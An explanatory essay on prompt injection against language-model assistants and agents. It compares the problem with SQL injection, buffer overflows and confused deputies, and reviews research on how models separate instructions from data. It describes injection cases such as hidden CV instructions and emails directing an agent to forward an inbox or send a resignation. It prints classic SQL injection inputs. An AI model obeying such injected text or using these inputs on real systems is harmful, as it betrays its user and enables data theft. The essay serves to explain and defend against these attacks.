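# Program Rules, Learned Behaviour and the Limits of Guarantees Against Prompt Injection

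## What prompt injection is and what blocking it would mean

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a language model, a program that has learned from large amounts of text how to continue whatever text it receives. The attacker writes something the model will read while working, such as an email or a web page, and words it so that the model acts on it as an instruction. The attacker does not need to break into the system or steal a password, and often needs no technical skill beyond writing a clear sentence.

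The weakness became widely known in 2022. Since then developers have made the attack harder, but none has shown how to make a model immune to it. That difference matters because an email program that leaks its owner's correspondence once in a thousand hostile messages is much less secure than one that cannot leak it.

### What the model reads

A language model reads and writes text in tokens, each a word or a piece of a word. It takes in a sequence of tokens, computes which token is likely to come next, adds one to the sequence, and repeats until the answer is complete. All the text it takes in at each step is called its context.

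The question a user has just typed into a chatbot is often a small part of the context, though users naturally think of it as the whole. The context begins with the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions, which cover what the product is for, what tone to take and which subjects to decline. It also includes earlier turns of the conversation and any documents, search results or messages that the software has fetched. The model receives all of this as a single sequence, although the people who wrote it may never have met and may want opposite things.

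On its own, a model only produces text. Developers let it do more by connecting it to tools, which are functions of ordinary software such as a web search, a calendar or an email account. The system prompt describes the tools and the format for requesting them. When the model's output contains such a request, the surrounding program carries it out and adds the result to the context as more text for the model to read. A model connected to tools in this way is an agent. The term has no settled definition, according to *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), a brief from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body of AI developers. The brief offers a workable one: software that uses outside tools to pursue a goal for its user.

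### Direct and indirect injection

In 2022 a developer could build a translation service by sending GPT-3, a language model to which OpenAI sold access, a one-line request to translate followed by whatever the customer typed. In September of that year Riley Goodside showed on Twitter that a customer could type a competing instruction instead of text to translate, and that GPT-3 would follow it. A day later Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, argued that this was a security hole and proposed the name "prompt injection". He modelled the name on SQL injection, an older attack in which someone enters database commands where a program expects a name or an address. Programmers now prevent that attack with parameterised queries. Willison (2025) later acknowledged that a Twitter user called @himbodhisattva had already used the phrase "prompt injection" on 13 May 2022.

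Within days, people publicly demonstrated prompt injection on a recruitment start-up's Twitter bot, which used GPT-3 to answer any post mentioning remote work. Willison collected examples of people getting the bot to repeat its own instructions and, in one case, to threaten the president.

In these cases the attacker wrote to the application directly, which security writers call direct prompt injection. The customer of a translation service has some authority over it, since the service exists to translate what the customer supplies, but the customer has no authority to replace the developer's instructions.

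In indirect prompt injection, the attacker does not need to interact with the application. In February 2023, when companies had begun to let language models read search results, web pages and mail, Greshake, Endres and colleagues described in *Not what you've signed up for* how an attacker can plant instructions in material that a model is likely to retrieve. When a user asks an ordinary question, the software fetches the planted text and adds it to the context with everything else. The attacker can leave the text on a public page for a search to find, send it by email, or trick a user into pasting it. A short first instruction can also direct the model to fetch a longer one from elsewhere.

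Greshake and colleagues tried such attacks on code-completion tools, on applications they had built for the purpose, and on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant built on GPT-4. Bing Chat could read the page open in the user's browser, and they found that text on the page could steer it even when the text was invisible to the user. The dangers they listed included theft of personal data, fraud, false summaries, and messages that spread themselves through email assistants that both read and send mail. They also observed that an attacker might only need to state a goal and could leave the model to work out the steps.

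The mechanism operates even without an attacker. In *Prompt injection*, his collected posts on the subject, Willison describes a case from June 2024. A developer had built a chatbot that answered questions by looking up passages in the documentation for one of Willison's programs. When asked about the meaning of life, the chatbot replied as a witty gerbil, because it had retrieved release notes containing an example prompt that asked a model to play a gerbil.

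Usage of the term varies. The Frontier Model Forum counts both direct and indirect injection. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) covers only instructions in external content that aim at something the user did not ask for, which excludes the direct form. The narrower usage still covers most of the danger for agents, since a customer who subverts his own translation just gets a bad translation, while indirect injection puts somebody else's mail or money at risk.

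### Jailbreaking

People often confuse prompt injection with jailbreaking, in which a user tries to get a model to break the rules its maker trained into it, for example to obtain instructions for a crime. In March 2024 Willison proposed that an attack is prompt injection only if someone has joined trusted text to untrusted text. By this test, a user who talks a model into a forbidden answer, with no trusted text added to the user's own, has not carried out a prompt injection.

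The difference between jailbreaks and prompt injection matters in practice because it affects detection. A jailbreak is usually recognizable from its content, since the user is asking for something forbidden, but an injected instruction may look ordinary. A stranger could steal the latest sales figures by emailing an instruction to forward them to an outside address, and the wording can be identical to a legitimate request from the account's owner. Willison therefore warns that a detector its vendor has trained on known jailbreaks may catch openly forbidden requests but miss this kind of theft.

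Prompt injection and jailbreaking overlap. Many chat products keep some of their safety rules in the system prompt, so a user who overrides that prompt does both at once. Attackers can also use jailbreaking techniques to get injected text past a model's defences.

### A recruiting tool and an email assistant

*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, describes a tool for recruiters. The developer instructs the model to score CVs on whether they meet a job's requirements, and the software adds each candidate's CV to the context in turn. One candidate has included a line, invisible to a human reader, asking for approval. If the model acts on that line, the candidate has in effect decided their own score. The tool only reads and scores CVs and has no access to email or money, but a better applicant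 could still lose an interview as a result.

Job candidates have tried this. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the security company Barracuda gave, as one real-world example, a résumé containing a hidden instruction for a screening tool to award ten out of ten.

Suppose an email assistant can read, forward and delete messages, and its owner asks for a summary of the morning's mail. One message, from a stranger, contains instructions to forward the contents of the inbox to an outside address and then delete the originals. The owner gave the assistant permission to forward and delete messages for other purposes. If the assistant follows the instructions, the stranger can use that permission knowing only the owner's email address.

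OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a very similar case from the company's own testing. OpenAI had trained a language model to look for weaknesses in the agent inside its Atlas browser, and this automated attacker planted an email in a test inbox. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email, treated its contents as authoritative, and sent the user's resignation to the chief executive. OpenAI then trained a new version of the agent against this class of attack.

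A prompt injection can work without looking like a command. In 2025, outside researchers reported one such email to OpenAI. It read like routine office correspondence about a restructuring and included a request to pass an employee's details to a supposed compliance system. In tests where the user had asked ChatGPT for thorough research on the day's mail, the attack worked half the time.

The attacker does not always want the assistant to do something beyond its job. Mascellino reports on an email campaign that Barracuda described in October 2026 without saying how widespread it was. The campaign paired a password-protected attachment for the human reader with hidden text for the assistant. The hidden text was meant to make the assistant's summary present the email as legitimate or urgent, so that the owner would open it.

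### Three meanings of "blocked"

A vendor who says a product blocks prompt injection might mean any of three things, each of which needs its own evidence: that hostile text never reaches the model (exclusion), that the model reads it but does not act on it (resistance), or that the model may act on it but no harm can follow (containment).

Exclusion is easy to guarantee for hidden text. Barracuda advises stripping hidden elements and invisible characters from content before an AI system reads it, which ordinary code can do to every message. This would remove the candidate's invisible line, but not the same request in plain type on the second page. A filter can catch the visible request only by recognising its meaning. OpenAI reports that well-developed attacks usually get past such filters, because detecting them is as hard as detecting a lie, often without the context that would expose it.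 David C notes that lists of forbidden phrases are no more effective, since an attacker can reword a request endlessly.

A cruder method is to keep out all text from strangers. The Frontier Model Forum suggests, as one option, limiting an email agent to messages from trusted senders. This limit makes the agent safer but much less useful. The recruiting tool could not adopt it, because its purpose is to read documents from strangers.

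Most people probably take "blocked" to mean resistance. The assistant reads the stranger's message, perhaps mentions the odd request in it, and carries on with the summary. Developers have worked hard at this, partly by training models to prioritize the developer's and the user's instructions over anything in retrieved material. The work has had results. OpenAI says the agent refuses in most of the attacks on ChatGPT that the company knows of.

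A guarantee against prompt injection would have to hold for every message anyone could write, in any language or disguise and with any surrounding text, not just for known attacks. OpenAI concedes that the nature of prompt injection "makes deterministic security guarantees challenging" and thinks the problem is unlikely ever to be fully solved. David C argues that there may never be a complete fix of the kind that exists for SQL injection, because a model only ever predicts the next token and has no built-in division between instructions and data. That claim about how models work needs more support than a short post can give it.

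It is also unclear what counts as resisting prompt injection. When a model scores a CV, the CV should affect the score, but a candidate's instruction about what score to give should not. A sentence claiming that the applicant meets every requirement of the job falls somewhere in between, and a recruiter might reasonably want the model to consider it with some doubt.

Containment starts from the assumption that resistance will sometimes fail. Suppose the stranger's message succeeds and the model outputs a request to forward the inbox. That output is only text, and the surrounding program does not have to carry it out. If the program sends mail only to addresses the owner has approved in advance, it will not forward the inbox to the stranger. Ordinary code enforces this limit, so it holds whatever the model outputs.

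OpenAI compares the problem to customer service, where some customers will deceive the staff, so a sensible employer has its systems cap the refunds that any one employee can give. ChatGPT has a similar safeguard, designed to detect when information from a conversation is about to go to a third party. It then either shows the user what would be sent and asks for confirmation, or stops the transmission.

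So a defender can have firm assurances of this kind without solving the problem of resistance, but each assurance covers only a particular harm. A list of approved addresses stops the assistant from forwarding mail to strangers, but not from deleting mail, which needs its own limit, or from presenting a phishing email as urgent in a summary. The recruiting tool is harder to protect because its only output is a score, and no code outside the model can distinguish a score the candidate earned from one the candidate dictated. The recruiter can require a person to read every CV before anyone decides on it, which contains the damage but brings back much of the work the tool was meant to save.

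## How ordinary programs keep commands and data apart

The list of approved addresses that stops an email assistant from forwarding mail to strangers is a few lines of ordinary program code. Because of how a machine carries out a rule, no message a stranger writes can get around those lines.

### What a rule is to a machine

Programmers write such a rule as a branch that sends the message if the recipient is on the list and refuses otherwise. When the program reaches the branch, it compares the recipient's address with those on the list, character by character. The result is either true or false, and if it is false, the processor skips the instructions that send mail and runs the ones that report a refusal.

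The comparison uses only the address and the list, so nothing in the body of the email can change the result, whether it is a plea, a threat or a forged order from the chief executive. The same address and list always give the same result.

The condition is written in the code, so a programmer can read it, see what it depends on and test it. Suppose a shop's software refuses any refund above £50 and stores the amount in pence as a 32-bit number, which can take about 4.3 billion values. A tester might try £49.99, £50.00, £50.01 and perhaps a negative amount, leaving billions of amounts untested. But the condition "greater than 5,000" is true of every number above 5,000 because of what the comparison means. This is a small proof, and it covers amounts that nobody has tested.

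### Guarantees and the seL4 proof

A guarantee is a claim that a property holds for every input within stated assumptions, and it needs either a proof or a mechanism that enforces the property. A vendor's report that a product stopped ten thousand test attacks may be good evidence, but it is not a guarantee, because the next attack may be different.

Programmers have given guarantees for much more complicated things than a refund limit. The kernel of an operating system is the part that runs with unlimited access to the hardware, so a fault there can undermine everything else on the computer. Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues (2009), in *seL4*, described a kernel of 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly code (the processor's own instructions) and proved that the C code does what its specification requires. To their knowledge, nobody had done this before for a complete general-purpose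 kernel.

The code looks ordinary. For example, one function changes the priority of a running task. If the task is waiting in a queue, the function takes it out and checks whether it is ready to run. If it is ready, the function puts it in the queue for its new priority. If not, the function marks it as no longer queued. In every case, the function then records the new priority. A reader can list all three routes through the function.

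The specification describes in logical terms what each request to the kernel should do, but not how. To connect it to the C code, the researchers defined what it means for a state of the running program to match a state of the specification. They then proved that if the program goes from state *s* to state *s′*, and *s* matches a specification state *σ*, the specification allows a step from *σ* to some *σ′* that matches *s′*. Because this holds for every step the program can take, if the two start out matched, they stay matched however long the kernel runs, so a finite proof can cover an unlimited number of possible runs.

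A program called Isabelle/HOL checked the proof. The researchers' model lets a user's program change any memory it can reach in any way, so the proof covers malicious programs as well as honest and buggy ones. If the proof's assumptions hold, the kernel never crashes or gets stuck in an endless loop, and no malformed request can subvert it.

The proof holds only if its assumptions do. In 2009 it assumed that the hardware, the assembly code, about 1,200 lines of start-up code, and the compiler, which translates C into processor instructions, were all correct. The project's current list, seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, leaves out the compiler for some types of processor, because an automatic tool now verifies the compiler's output. The list still includes the other three, along with an assumption about devices that write to memory without going through the processor, since one of these could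 overwrite the kernel. The proof also no longer applies if a cosmic ray flips a bit in memory. A separate proof that secrets do not leak does not cover timing, so a program might still learn something from how long an operation takes.

Klein and colleagues also concede that a cynic might say the proof only shows that the code has the same bugs as the specification. No proof can show that the specification describes what people wanted. They reply that the specification is a third of the size of the C code and uses simpler concepts, so people have less to check by eye. That seems a fair reply, but it still relies partly on human judgement.

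### SQL injection, step by step

Most programs have no such proof, but they can still guarantee particular properties that some mechanism enforces, as in the standard defence against SQL injection.

SQL is a language in which programs send commands to a database. Imagine a website on which users keep lists of their belongings, an example adapted from MITRE's *CWE-89*, the entry for SQL injection in a public catalogue of software weaknesses. A user called wiley searches for a lamp, and the website's program sends the database this query:

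```
SELECT * FROM items WHERE owner = 'wiley' AND itemname = 'lamp'
```

The query asks for every row of the items table that belongs to wiley and has the name lamp. A careless programmer builds it by joining strings: some fixed text that ends in a quotation mark, then whatever the user typed, then a closing quotation mark. Now suppose wiley types this into the search box:

```
lamp' OR 'a'='a
```

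The joined string is then:

```
SELECT * FROM items WHERE owner = 'wiley' AND itemname = 'lamp' OR 'a'='a'
```

The database receives a single string, with no record of who wrote which part. Its parser, the component that works out the structure of a query, reads the quotation mark after "lamp" as the end of the name, and then reads OR and a further condition as part of the query. SQL groups AND before OR, so the query now matches rows that belong to wiley and are called lamp, or any row if the letter a equals the letter a. That is always true, so wiley gets everybody's items. On a server that accepts several commands in one string, wiley could also have added a command to delete them.

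One possible repair is to look for dangerous characters in the input. Banning quotation marks would shut out anyone called O'Reilly, as MITRE points out. Programmers can instead "escape" each quotation mark, marking it so that the database treats it as text. Su and Wassermann's *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications* describes a shop's web page that escapes everything the user enters but is still vulnerable. One field takes a card type as a number, and the query does not put numbers in quotation marks. A user can therefore enter `2 OR 1=1`, which has no quotation marks to escape, and get every card number in the database. In its *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, OWASP, a nonprofit foundation for software security, strongly discourages relying on escaping and does not guarantee that it will stop every attack.

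A parameterised query works differently. The programmer writes the query with placeholders where the values will go:

```
SELECT * FROM items WHERE owner = $1 AND itemname = $2
```

In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, the program can send this text in a Parse message. The server then parses the query as a request for the rows where two comparisons both hold. The values come afterwards in a separate Bind message, which supplies wiley for the first placeholder and the search text for the second. If the search text is `lamp' OR 'a'='a`, the server looks for an item whose name is exactly those fifteen characters. It finds none, and wiley gets an empty list. The quotation marks don't change the query's structure because the server has already finished parsing it.

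This works for every string, and Su and Wassermann's definition of an attack helps explain why. A parser represents a query as a tree, with the whole query at the root and the individual names, values and operators at the leaves. In a legitimate query, each piece of user input fills one node, meaning that it makes up all the text under that node and nothing else. Su and Wassermann count a query as an injection attack if it parses correctly but some piece of input does not fill a single node of a kind that the programmer allows. Wiley's input is an attack by this definition, because part of it belongs to a name and the rest forms a new condition. In a parameterised query, the tree exists before the input arrives and the input can only fill the placeholder's position, so the defender does not have to guess what attackers will try.

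Su and Wassermann also built a tool, SQLCHECK, for programs that still build queries by joining strings. It puts markers around each piece of user input, parses the finished query with the markers in place, and blocks the query if any input extends beyond its permitted node. In effect, the markers preserve provenance, the record of who supplied a piece of text, until the text could become a command. They proved that the method catches all attacks that meet their definition and nothing else. In tests on real web applications, the tool made no mistakes and took about three milliseconds per query. Both the proof and the tool rely on SQL's exact grammar, which lets a parser determine the structure of any query.

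Parameterised queries also rest on assumptions. The programmer has to use them everywhere, including in queries that reuse stored text, because an attacker can save a hostile string that another part of the program later joins into a query. The placeholders also have to be real, because some libraries imitate them by quoting the values and joining the strings themselves, which makes safety depend on the quoting again. A placeholder can only stand for a value, so a programmer cannot use one for a table name or the sort order. For those cases, OWASP recommends that the program compare the user's choice with a short list of expected values, take the matching table name from its own code, and report an error for anything else.

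### Code and data in one memory

Computer memory has an older version of the same problem. Nearly all computers keep a program's instructions in the same memory as the data it works on, and both are stored as numbers. A number acts as an instruction when the processor fetches it from the address of the next instruction.

Suppose a program in C sets aside 64 bytes for a user's name and copies in whatever arrives over the network. C does not check that the name fits, so a name that is too long overwrites the neighbouring memory. This is called a buffer overflow. The overwritten memory often contains a return address, which determines where the processor continues when the current function ends. An attacker can send a "name" containing processor instructions, padded so that its last bytes replace the return address with the location of those instructions. When the function ends, the processor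 executes the name as code. The Morris worm, which spread across the early internet in 1988, used an overflow of this kind.

Non-executable memory stops the processor from running data as instructions. Modern processors keep a permission bit for each block of memory, called the no-execute or NX bit, and the operating system sets it for blocks that hold data. If the processor tries to fetch an instruction from such a block, it raises a fault, and the operating system normally stops the program. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, Nvidia and several universities, lists NX bits and prepared statements, the usual form of parameterised query, as ways to enforce the separation of instructions and data.

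The NX bit achieves less, however. An attacker who has overwritten the return address can no longer run new instructions but can still send the processor to legitimate instructions already in the program's memory. In 1997 a programmer known as Solar Designer showed how to send it to an existing library function that starts other programs. Researchers later found ways to chain together short fragments of existing code to carry out almost any computation. The NX bit still prevents data from running as code in these attacks, but defenders need a broader guarantee.

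Mainstream processors and operating systems adopted NX bits in the early 2000s, some fifteen years after the worm, and engineers have added other defences before and since. Compilers can place a secret value next to the return address and check that it is intact before the function ends. Operating systems can load code at random locations, so that an attacker has to guess where to send the processor. Both measures help, but an attacker who can read the memory can learn the secret value and the locations. David C says that a newer defence, the Memory Tagging Extension in ARM processors, solves the problem at its root. This may be too generous, because the extension tags each small piece of memory and detects access through an address with a different tag, but there are only sixteen tags, so a stray address will sometimes match by chance.

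A program can eliminate overflows by checking on every write that the data fits. Many newer languages insert these checks automatically. A proof can also rule out overflows, and the seL4 project notes that its proof excludes them along with other common programming errors. Much older C code has neither. In MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), writing outside the intended area of memory ranks fifth, and three specific kinds of buffer overflow rank 11th, 14th and 16th. Those three are new to the list only because MITRE changed how it counts, according to its *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025).

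### The confused deputy

A program can keep commands and data perfectly separate and still carry out a command for the wrong person. Suppose the website took the owner's name from the search form instead of from the login. Any user could type somebody else's name, and a parameterised query would list that person's belongings. The query would have the structure the programmer intended, but the program would be using its own database access to show rows to someone with no right to see them.

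A program with legitimate powers that someone else can misuse in this way is called a confused deputy. The name comes from Hardy's 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*, which tells a story he called "nearly true". About eleven years earlier, he was at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler kept in a system directory called SYSX. The staff had given the compiler permission to write to files in that directory so that it could record statistics there. The directory also held the company's billing records. Customers could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one customer named the billing file. When the compiler tried to open it, the operating system found that the compiler had permission, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

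Hardy considers several repairs and finds a problem with each. The compiler could refuse to write outside the customer's own directory, but customers had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse to write debugging output to SYSX, but some people had legitimate access to files there. It could refuse to write to the billing file, identified by name, but SYSX contained other sensitive files, and somebody would have to change the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The general rules for opening a file also kept growing, and the last time Hardy wrote them down, he needed fourteen ANDs and ORs.

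In his view, the problem was that the compiler had authority from two sources, the customer who ran it and the staff who had installed it, and could not indicate which it was using when it opened a file. Tymshare added a way for a program to choose between the two, but some programs soon turned out to need more than two.

Hardy's solution was the capability, a token that both identifies a file and carries the right to use it. The compiler holds a capability for the statistics file, and a customer who wants debugging output must hand over a capability for the file that will receive it. Customers have no capability for the billing file, and typing its name does not give them one. The compiler does not need to inspect names or check permissions. UT Austin's *Confused Deputy* lecture slides give the file descriptor, a handle to one particular open file, as a modern equivalent.

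CVE Find's *CWE-441 Detail* reproduces the catalogue entry for this weakness, which attributes it to a program's failure to preserve the original source of a request. A capability deals with this by tying the authority to the request itself. This works because the compiler's programmer decides in advance which output goes with which capability, and no text from a customer can swap them. David C agrees that developers can fix a classical confused deputy, but calls language models "inherently confusable".

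### Bugs and the survival of SQL injection

Ordinary programs are full of faults, so this account may seem too flattering. SQL injection is an embarrassing example because developers have known about such flaws for decades and have effective ways to prevent them. In a joint alert with the FBI, CISA (2024), the US government's cybersecurity agency, described how attackers had exploited SQL injection flaws in a file-transfer product, affecting thousands of organisations. SQL injection rose from third in MITRE's 2024 ranking to second in the latest, for 2025, and the number of recorded cases rose by almost 1,000.

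David C, however, writes that SQL injection peaked around 2010 and is now rare in websites. His claim and MITRE's ranking can both be true, because MITRE uses 39,080 published vulnerability records, which cannot show what share of all products have the flaw. The total number of records also grew. OWASP's *The Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Risks* (2025) draws on tests of more than 2.8 million applications and measures the share with each kind of weakness. It describes SQL injection as low in frequency and high in impact, and ranks injection attacks in general fifth, down from third in 2021. SQL injection therefore seems to persist in a small share of a very large and growing body of software.

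The cause is typically that a programmer built a query by joining strings. Replacing that line with a parameterised query makes it safe against every input, including ones nobody has thought of. A company can also search its code for other queries built the same way and refuse to release a product that contains any. CISA and the FBI have similarly asked manufacturers to enforce parameterised queries across all their applications, according to Industrial Cyber's *CISA, FBI release secure by design alert*. Because this kind of bug breaks a stated rule, a reviewer can check the code against that rule.

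This reply fits Hardy's compiler less well. He insists that the code for debugging output was correct when the programmer wrote it, and that it became wrong when the staff gave the compiler its permission over SYSX. Nobody could point to a faulty line, because the trouble came from combining two reasonable decisions. The fix was to redesign how programs receive authority. But Hardy could work out exactly what had gone wrong, and the redesign worked for every file name a customer could type.

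### What no checker can do

There is also a mathematical limit. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no procedure can determine, for every program and every input, whether the program will eventually stop. Suppose such a procedure existed. Someone could then write a program that takes the text of any program, uses the procedure to find out whether that program would stop if given its own text, and runs forever if the answer is yes or stops if the answer is no. Given its own text, this new program would do the opposite of what the procedure predicts, so the procedure cannot exist. In 1953 Henry Rice extended the result to any property of what programs compute that some programs have and others lack. So nobody can build a tool that always reports correctly whether arbitrary software is secure in a given respect.

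These results rule out a single procedure that works for all programs, but it is still possible to prove things about one particular program, and a programmer can write it in a way that makes the proof easier. Klein and colleagues did this throughout their kernel. They left out features of C that make a program's path hard to follow, such as jumps to arbitrary points in the code. They also kept interrupts mostly switched off and did not try to handle several processors at once, because proofs about simultaneous activities are much harder. They proved, among other things, that every request to the kernel finishes, a property that Turing showed to be undecidable in general.

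These restrictions did not make the kernel slow. Passing a message from one program to another took 224 processor cycles, against 206 for a hand-tuned version of a comparable kernel, though the researchers had not yet added the optimised code to the verified version. The proof took much more work, running to about 200,000 lines including supporting libraries. Developers can reduce this work by keeping the part that needs a guarantee small. If an email program sends every outgoing message through a check for approved addresses, its developers have to verify the check and make sure nothing can bypass it, but they do not have to prove the rest of the program correct.

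## How a language model decides which text to obey

In a parameterised query, the database parses the command before it receives a stranger's text. A language model instead takes in the developer's rules and a stranger's email as one sequence, and uses all of it to compute the next token.

### One email, from text to probabilities

Zverev, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2024), in *Can LLMs Separate Instructions from Data?*, give an example without an attacker. They simulated an email client with Microsoft's Phi-3-medium. They told the model that it could summarise emails and send them at the user's request, but should never answer requests or commands found in the emails. They then asked it to summarise a set of emails. In one, Daniel, who was planning a team-building event, asked the recipient to reply urgently with the subject "Confirm". The model's output included a request to send that reply.

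The surrounding software first joins the instructions and the emails into one string and cuts the string into tokens. Each token has a number, which picks out a row in a table. The row is a vector, a list of numbers that training has fixed (4,096 of them in Llama 3.1 8B, a mid-sized model from Meta). All tokens use the same table, so "send" gets the same vector in the developer's sentence about sending emails as in Daniel's request to send one back. Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, point out that nothing in the vector marks it as trusted or untrusted. The model also receives each token's position in the sequence, but the position does not identify who wrote the token.

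The vectors then pass through a stack of layers, 32 of them in Llama 3.1 8B. In each layer, a step called attention lets every token's vector take in information from the tokens before it. The model multiplies each vector by matrices of learned weights to get a query, a key and a value. To update position i, it compares that position's query with the key at each earlier position j:

```
score(i, j) = (query_i · key_j) / √d
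```

Here d is the length of the query. The score is high when the query and the key point in similar directions. A standard formula turns the scores into positive weights that add up to 1, and the model adds up the values in proportion to those weights. At the last position, where the next token will come from, the sum looks like this:

```
  sum of weight × value over the developer's tokens
+ sum of weight × value over the email's tokens
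```

Pant and colleagues write the sum in two parts to show where the email enters the calculation, but the model computes a single total, which the next layer uses. If 70% of the weight falls on the developer's tokens and 30% on Daniel's, both affect the total, but it does not record those proportions.

After the last layer, the model compares the final vector with every token in its vocabulary (about 128,000 in Llama 3.1) and gives each one a probability. One token might begin a summary and another a request to send mail. The software picks a token, adds it to the sequence and runs the calculation again.

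The code that does all this is short and consists mostly of multiplications and additions. No line in it tests whether an instruction came from the developer. In the email program with a list of approved addresses, the body of a message could not affect the result of the check. In the model, every token of Daniel's message is an input to the calculation that produces the request to send mail. The developer's rule about ignoring requests in emails is an input of the same kind.

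### Where obedience comes from

A newly built model does not follow instructions, even from its developer. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) notes that an early model given the question "What is 1+1?" might have replied "What is 2+2?", because questions often come in lists. Developers changed this by training models on many examples of instructions followed by good responses, adjusting the weights until such responses became likely.

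Developers also added role tags, special tokens that the software places around each stretch of text to mark it as the system prompt, the user's message, the model's own output or the result of a tool. Because the software inserts these tags, a stranger cannot type a real one in a well-built application. Still, like any other token, a tag has a vector in the model's embedding table, and training determines how much it affects the text around it. Developers train models to give some roles priority over others, but the models only tend to follow that priority.

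A language model has no stored list of people whose instructions it should follow, so how likely it is to obey a request depends on the whole context. It might ignore Daniel's request in one inbox and act on it in another where the wording is more urgent or the surrounding emails are longer.

### Testing the "inherently confusable deputy"

David C argues from this design that a model which only predicts the next token does not distinguish instructions from data. In his view, detecting injections, training models to prefer instructions over data, and marking data in the prompt are all attempts to add this distinction to a technology that lacks it. He concludes that developers should treat the model as a deputy they cannot make immune to confusion, and that the remaining risk is too high for some systems.

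The comparison with Hardy's compiler holds up to a point. Capabilities fixed the compiler by tying authority to each request. To copy this fix, a model would need a way to carry the authority of each sentence's author through the layers and a step that rejects sentences without enough authority, but the calculation above has neither.

However, the argument rests on a hasty inference from what a model outputs to what it computes internally. Predicting the next line of a play is much easier for a system that keeps track of who is speaking. A model trained only to predict text could therefore learn to represent the source of a passage, and researchers can check whether it has.

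Language models do learn to distinguish instructions from data, to some extent. In *ASIDE*, Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues (2025) trained simple classifiers to tell instruction tokens from data tokens using the vectors inside several models. They chose prompts in which individual words would not reveal the answer. In ordinary models, the classifiers could not reliably separate the two kinds of token in the first layers, but they could after several layers. So the distinction is missing from the table of vectors and appears later in the calculation.

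Ye and colleagues tested what this sense of role depends on and found that writing like a user had much more effect than the tag. They wrapped the same passages of ordinary web text in the tags for each of five roles, then trained a classifier to tell from the model's internal vectors which tags were in use. Because the passages didn't differ between roles, the classifier could learn only the effect of the tags. They then applied it to 200 real conversations in each of four models. When text written by users had its proper user tags, the classifier identified it as user text. When the researchers put the same text inside tool tags, as happens when a command arrives in a web page, the classifier still gave it a 76–88% probability of being user text, depending on the model, and never more than a 20% probability of being tool output.

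Simply stating who was speaking also had an effect. The researchers placed the same command to leak a file inside 212 different framings, some of which declared that the text came from the user. Those framings made up 24% of the total, but all of the 5% in which the command registered most strongly as user text. Over 1,000 attempts, an agent carried out the command 2% of the time in the group where it registered least as user text and 70% in the group where it registered most.

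Ye and colleagues used a classifier trained on tags alone to show that style pushes the vectors in the same direction as a tag, and more strongly. They conclude that the boundary between roles does not exist inside the model, but their result does not show that the information about the real tag has gone, and the classifiers in *ASIDE* suggest that some of it can be recovered. The models' behaviour also suggests that they draw some distinction between roles. When the researchers hid an ordinary injected command in a web page, all but one of the models they tested followed it in at most 2% of attempts, and the exception did so in 26%. Ye and colleagues attribute the low rates to models having memorised familiar attacks, which is plausible, but a system that drew no distinction at all would follow the command far more often.

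David C's claim that a language model is an inherently confusable deputy is therefore right about the architecture but too strong about behaviour. Models do learn to treat a stranger's text differently, but they rely partly on cues the stranger controls, such as phrasing and claims of identity, so they can still be confused. Whether this weakness is inherent depends on whether engineers can build a model without it.

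### Randomness, opacity and the missing specification

People often explain the lack of a guarantee by saying that language models are random. The randomness is real, but it is the easiest part of the problem to remove. It enters when the software picks a token. The model gives each candidate token a score z, and the software converts scores into probabilities with a setting called temperature, T:

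```
probability of token i = exp(z_i / T) / (sum of exp(z_j / T) over all tokens j)
```

Suppose that only two tokens have a serious chance after Daniel's email. The one that begins a summary scores 2, and the one that begins a request to send mail scores 0. At temperature 1, the software picks the request 12% of the time. At temperature 0.5 it does so less than 2% of the time. At temperature zero it always takes the token with the highest score, so it always begins a summary. (Rounding differences can still creep in when a server handles many requests together, but engineers can eliminate those too.)

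If Daniel words his email differently, the scores might become 1.0 for the summary and 1.2 for the request. At temperature 1, the assistant would then make the mistake of sending the mail 55% of the time. Temperature zero makes the model perfectly repeatable, so it would make that mistake in every run.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* also points out that a model that always gives the same output for the same input can still produce a forbidden action when an attacker changes the input. Repeatability lets a tester reproduce a failure and study it, but tests at temperature zero still cover only the texts that someone has tried. Pant and colleagues use this gap between tested and untested text as one step in a proof that no defence inside such a model can be perfect.

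A system that relies on randomness can also have a guarantee. Cryptography depends on random keys, and its security claims allow a tiny chance that an attacker guesses one. Engineers accept those claims because cryptographers have stated exactly what must not happen and calculated a bound on its probability, assuming that certain mathematical problems are hard.

A language model is also opaque. A programmer can read the condition in a refund program and see that it covers every amount above £50, whereas nobody can read eight billion weights that way. Anyone can inspect the weights of an open model such as Llama and follow each multiplication, but doing so does not reveal a condition that a person can check. Classifiers like those of Ye and colleagues give a partial view of how the model works.

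Even if researchers could describe exactly how a model separates text it will obey from text it won't, they would still need a specification of which text it ought to obey before they could prove it secure. The seL4 researchers had a specification to prove their C code against, but no equivalent exists for a model. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, this is the problem with using a second model to approve the first model's actions: no formal specification lists which actions the second model should allow after which events, so nobody can prove that it implements the intended policy.

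Some narrow properties are easy to specify precisely, such as "The model never outputs a request to send mail to an address that is not on this list." Because large models are opaque, nobody knows how to prove from the weights that such a property holds in every possible context. Developers rarely need that proof, since a few lines of code outside the model can check the address. But people want a broader property, that the model follows the instructions it should follow and no others, and there is no precise specification for it.

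### A definition and a score

Zverev, Abdelnabi and colleagues tried to supply part of that specification. They describe a language model as a function g with two inputs, an instruction and some data. To measure how well it separates them, they take a task s, some data d, and an unrelated command x, which they call a probe. They run the model once with the probe in the data and once with the probe in the instruction, and measure how much the outputs differ:

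```
separation = average of D( g(s, x + d), g(s + x, d) )
```

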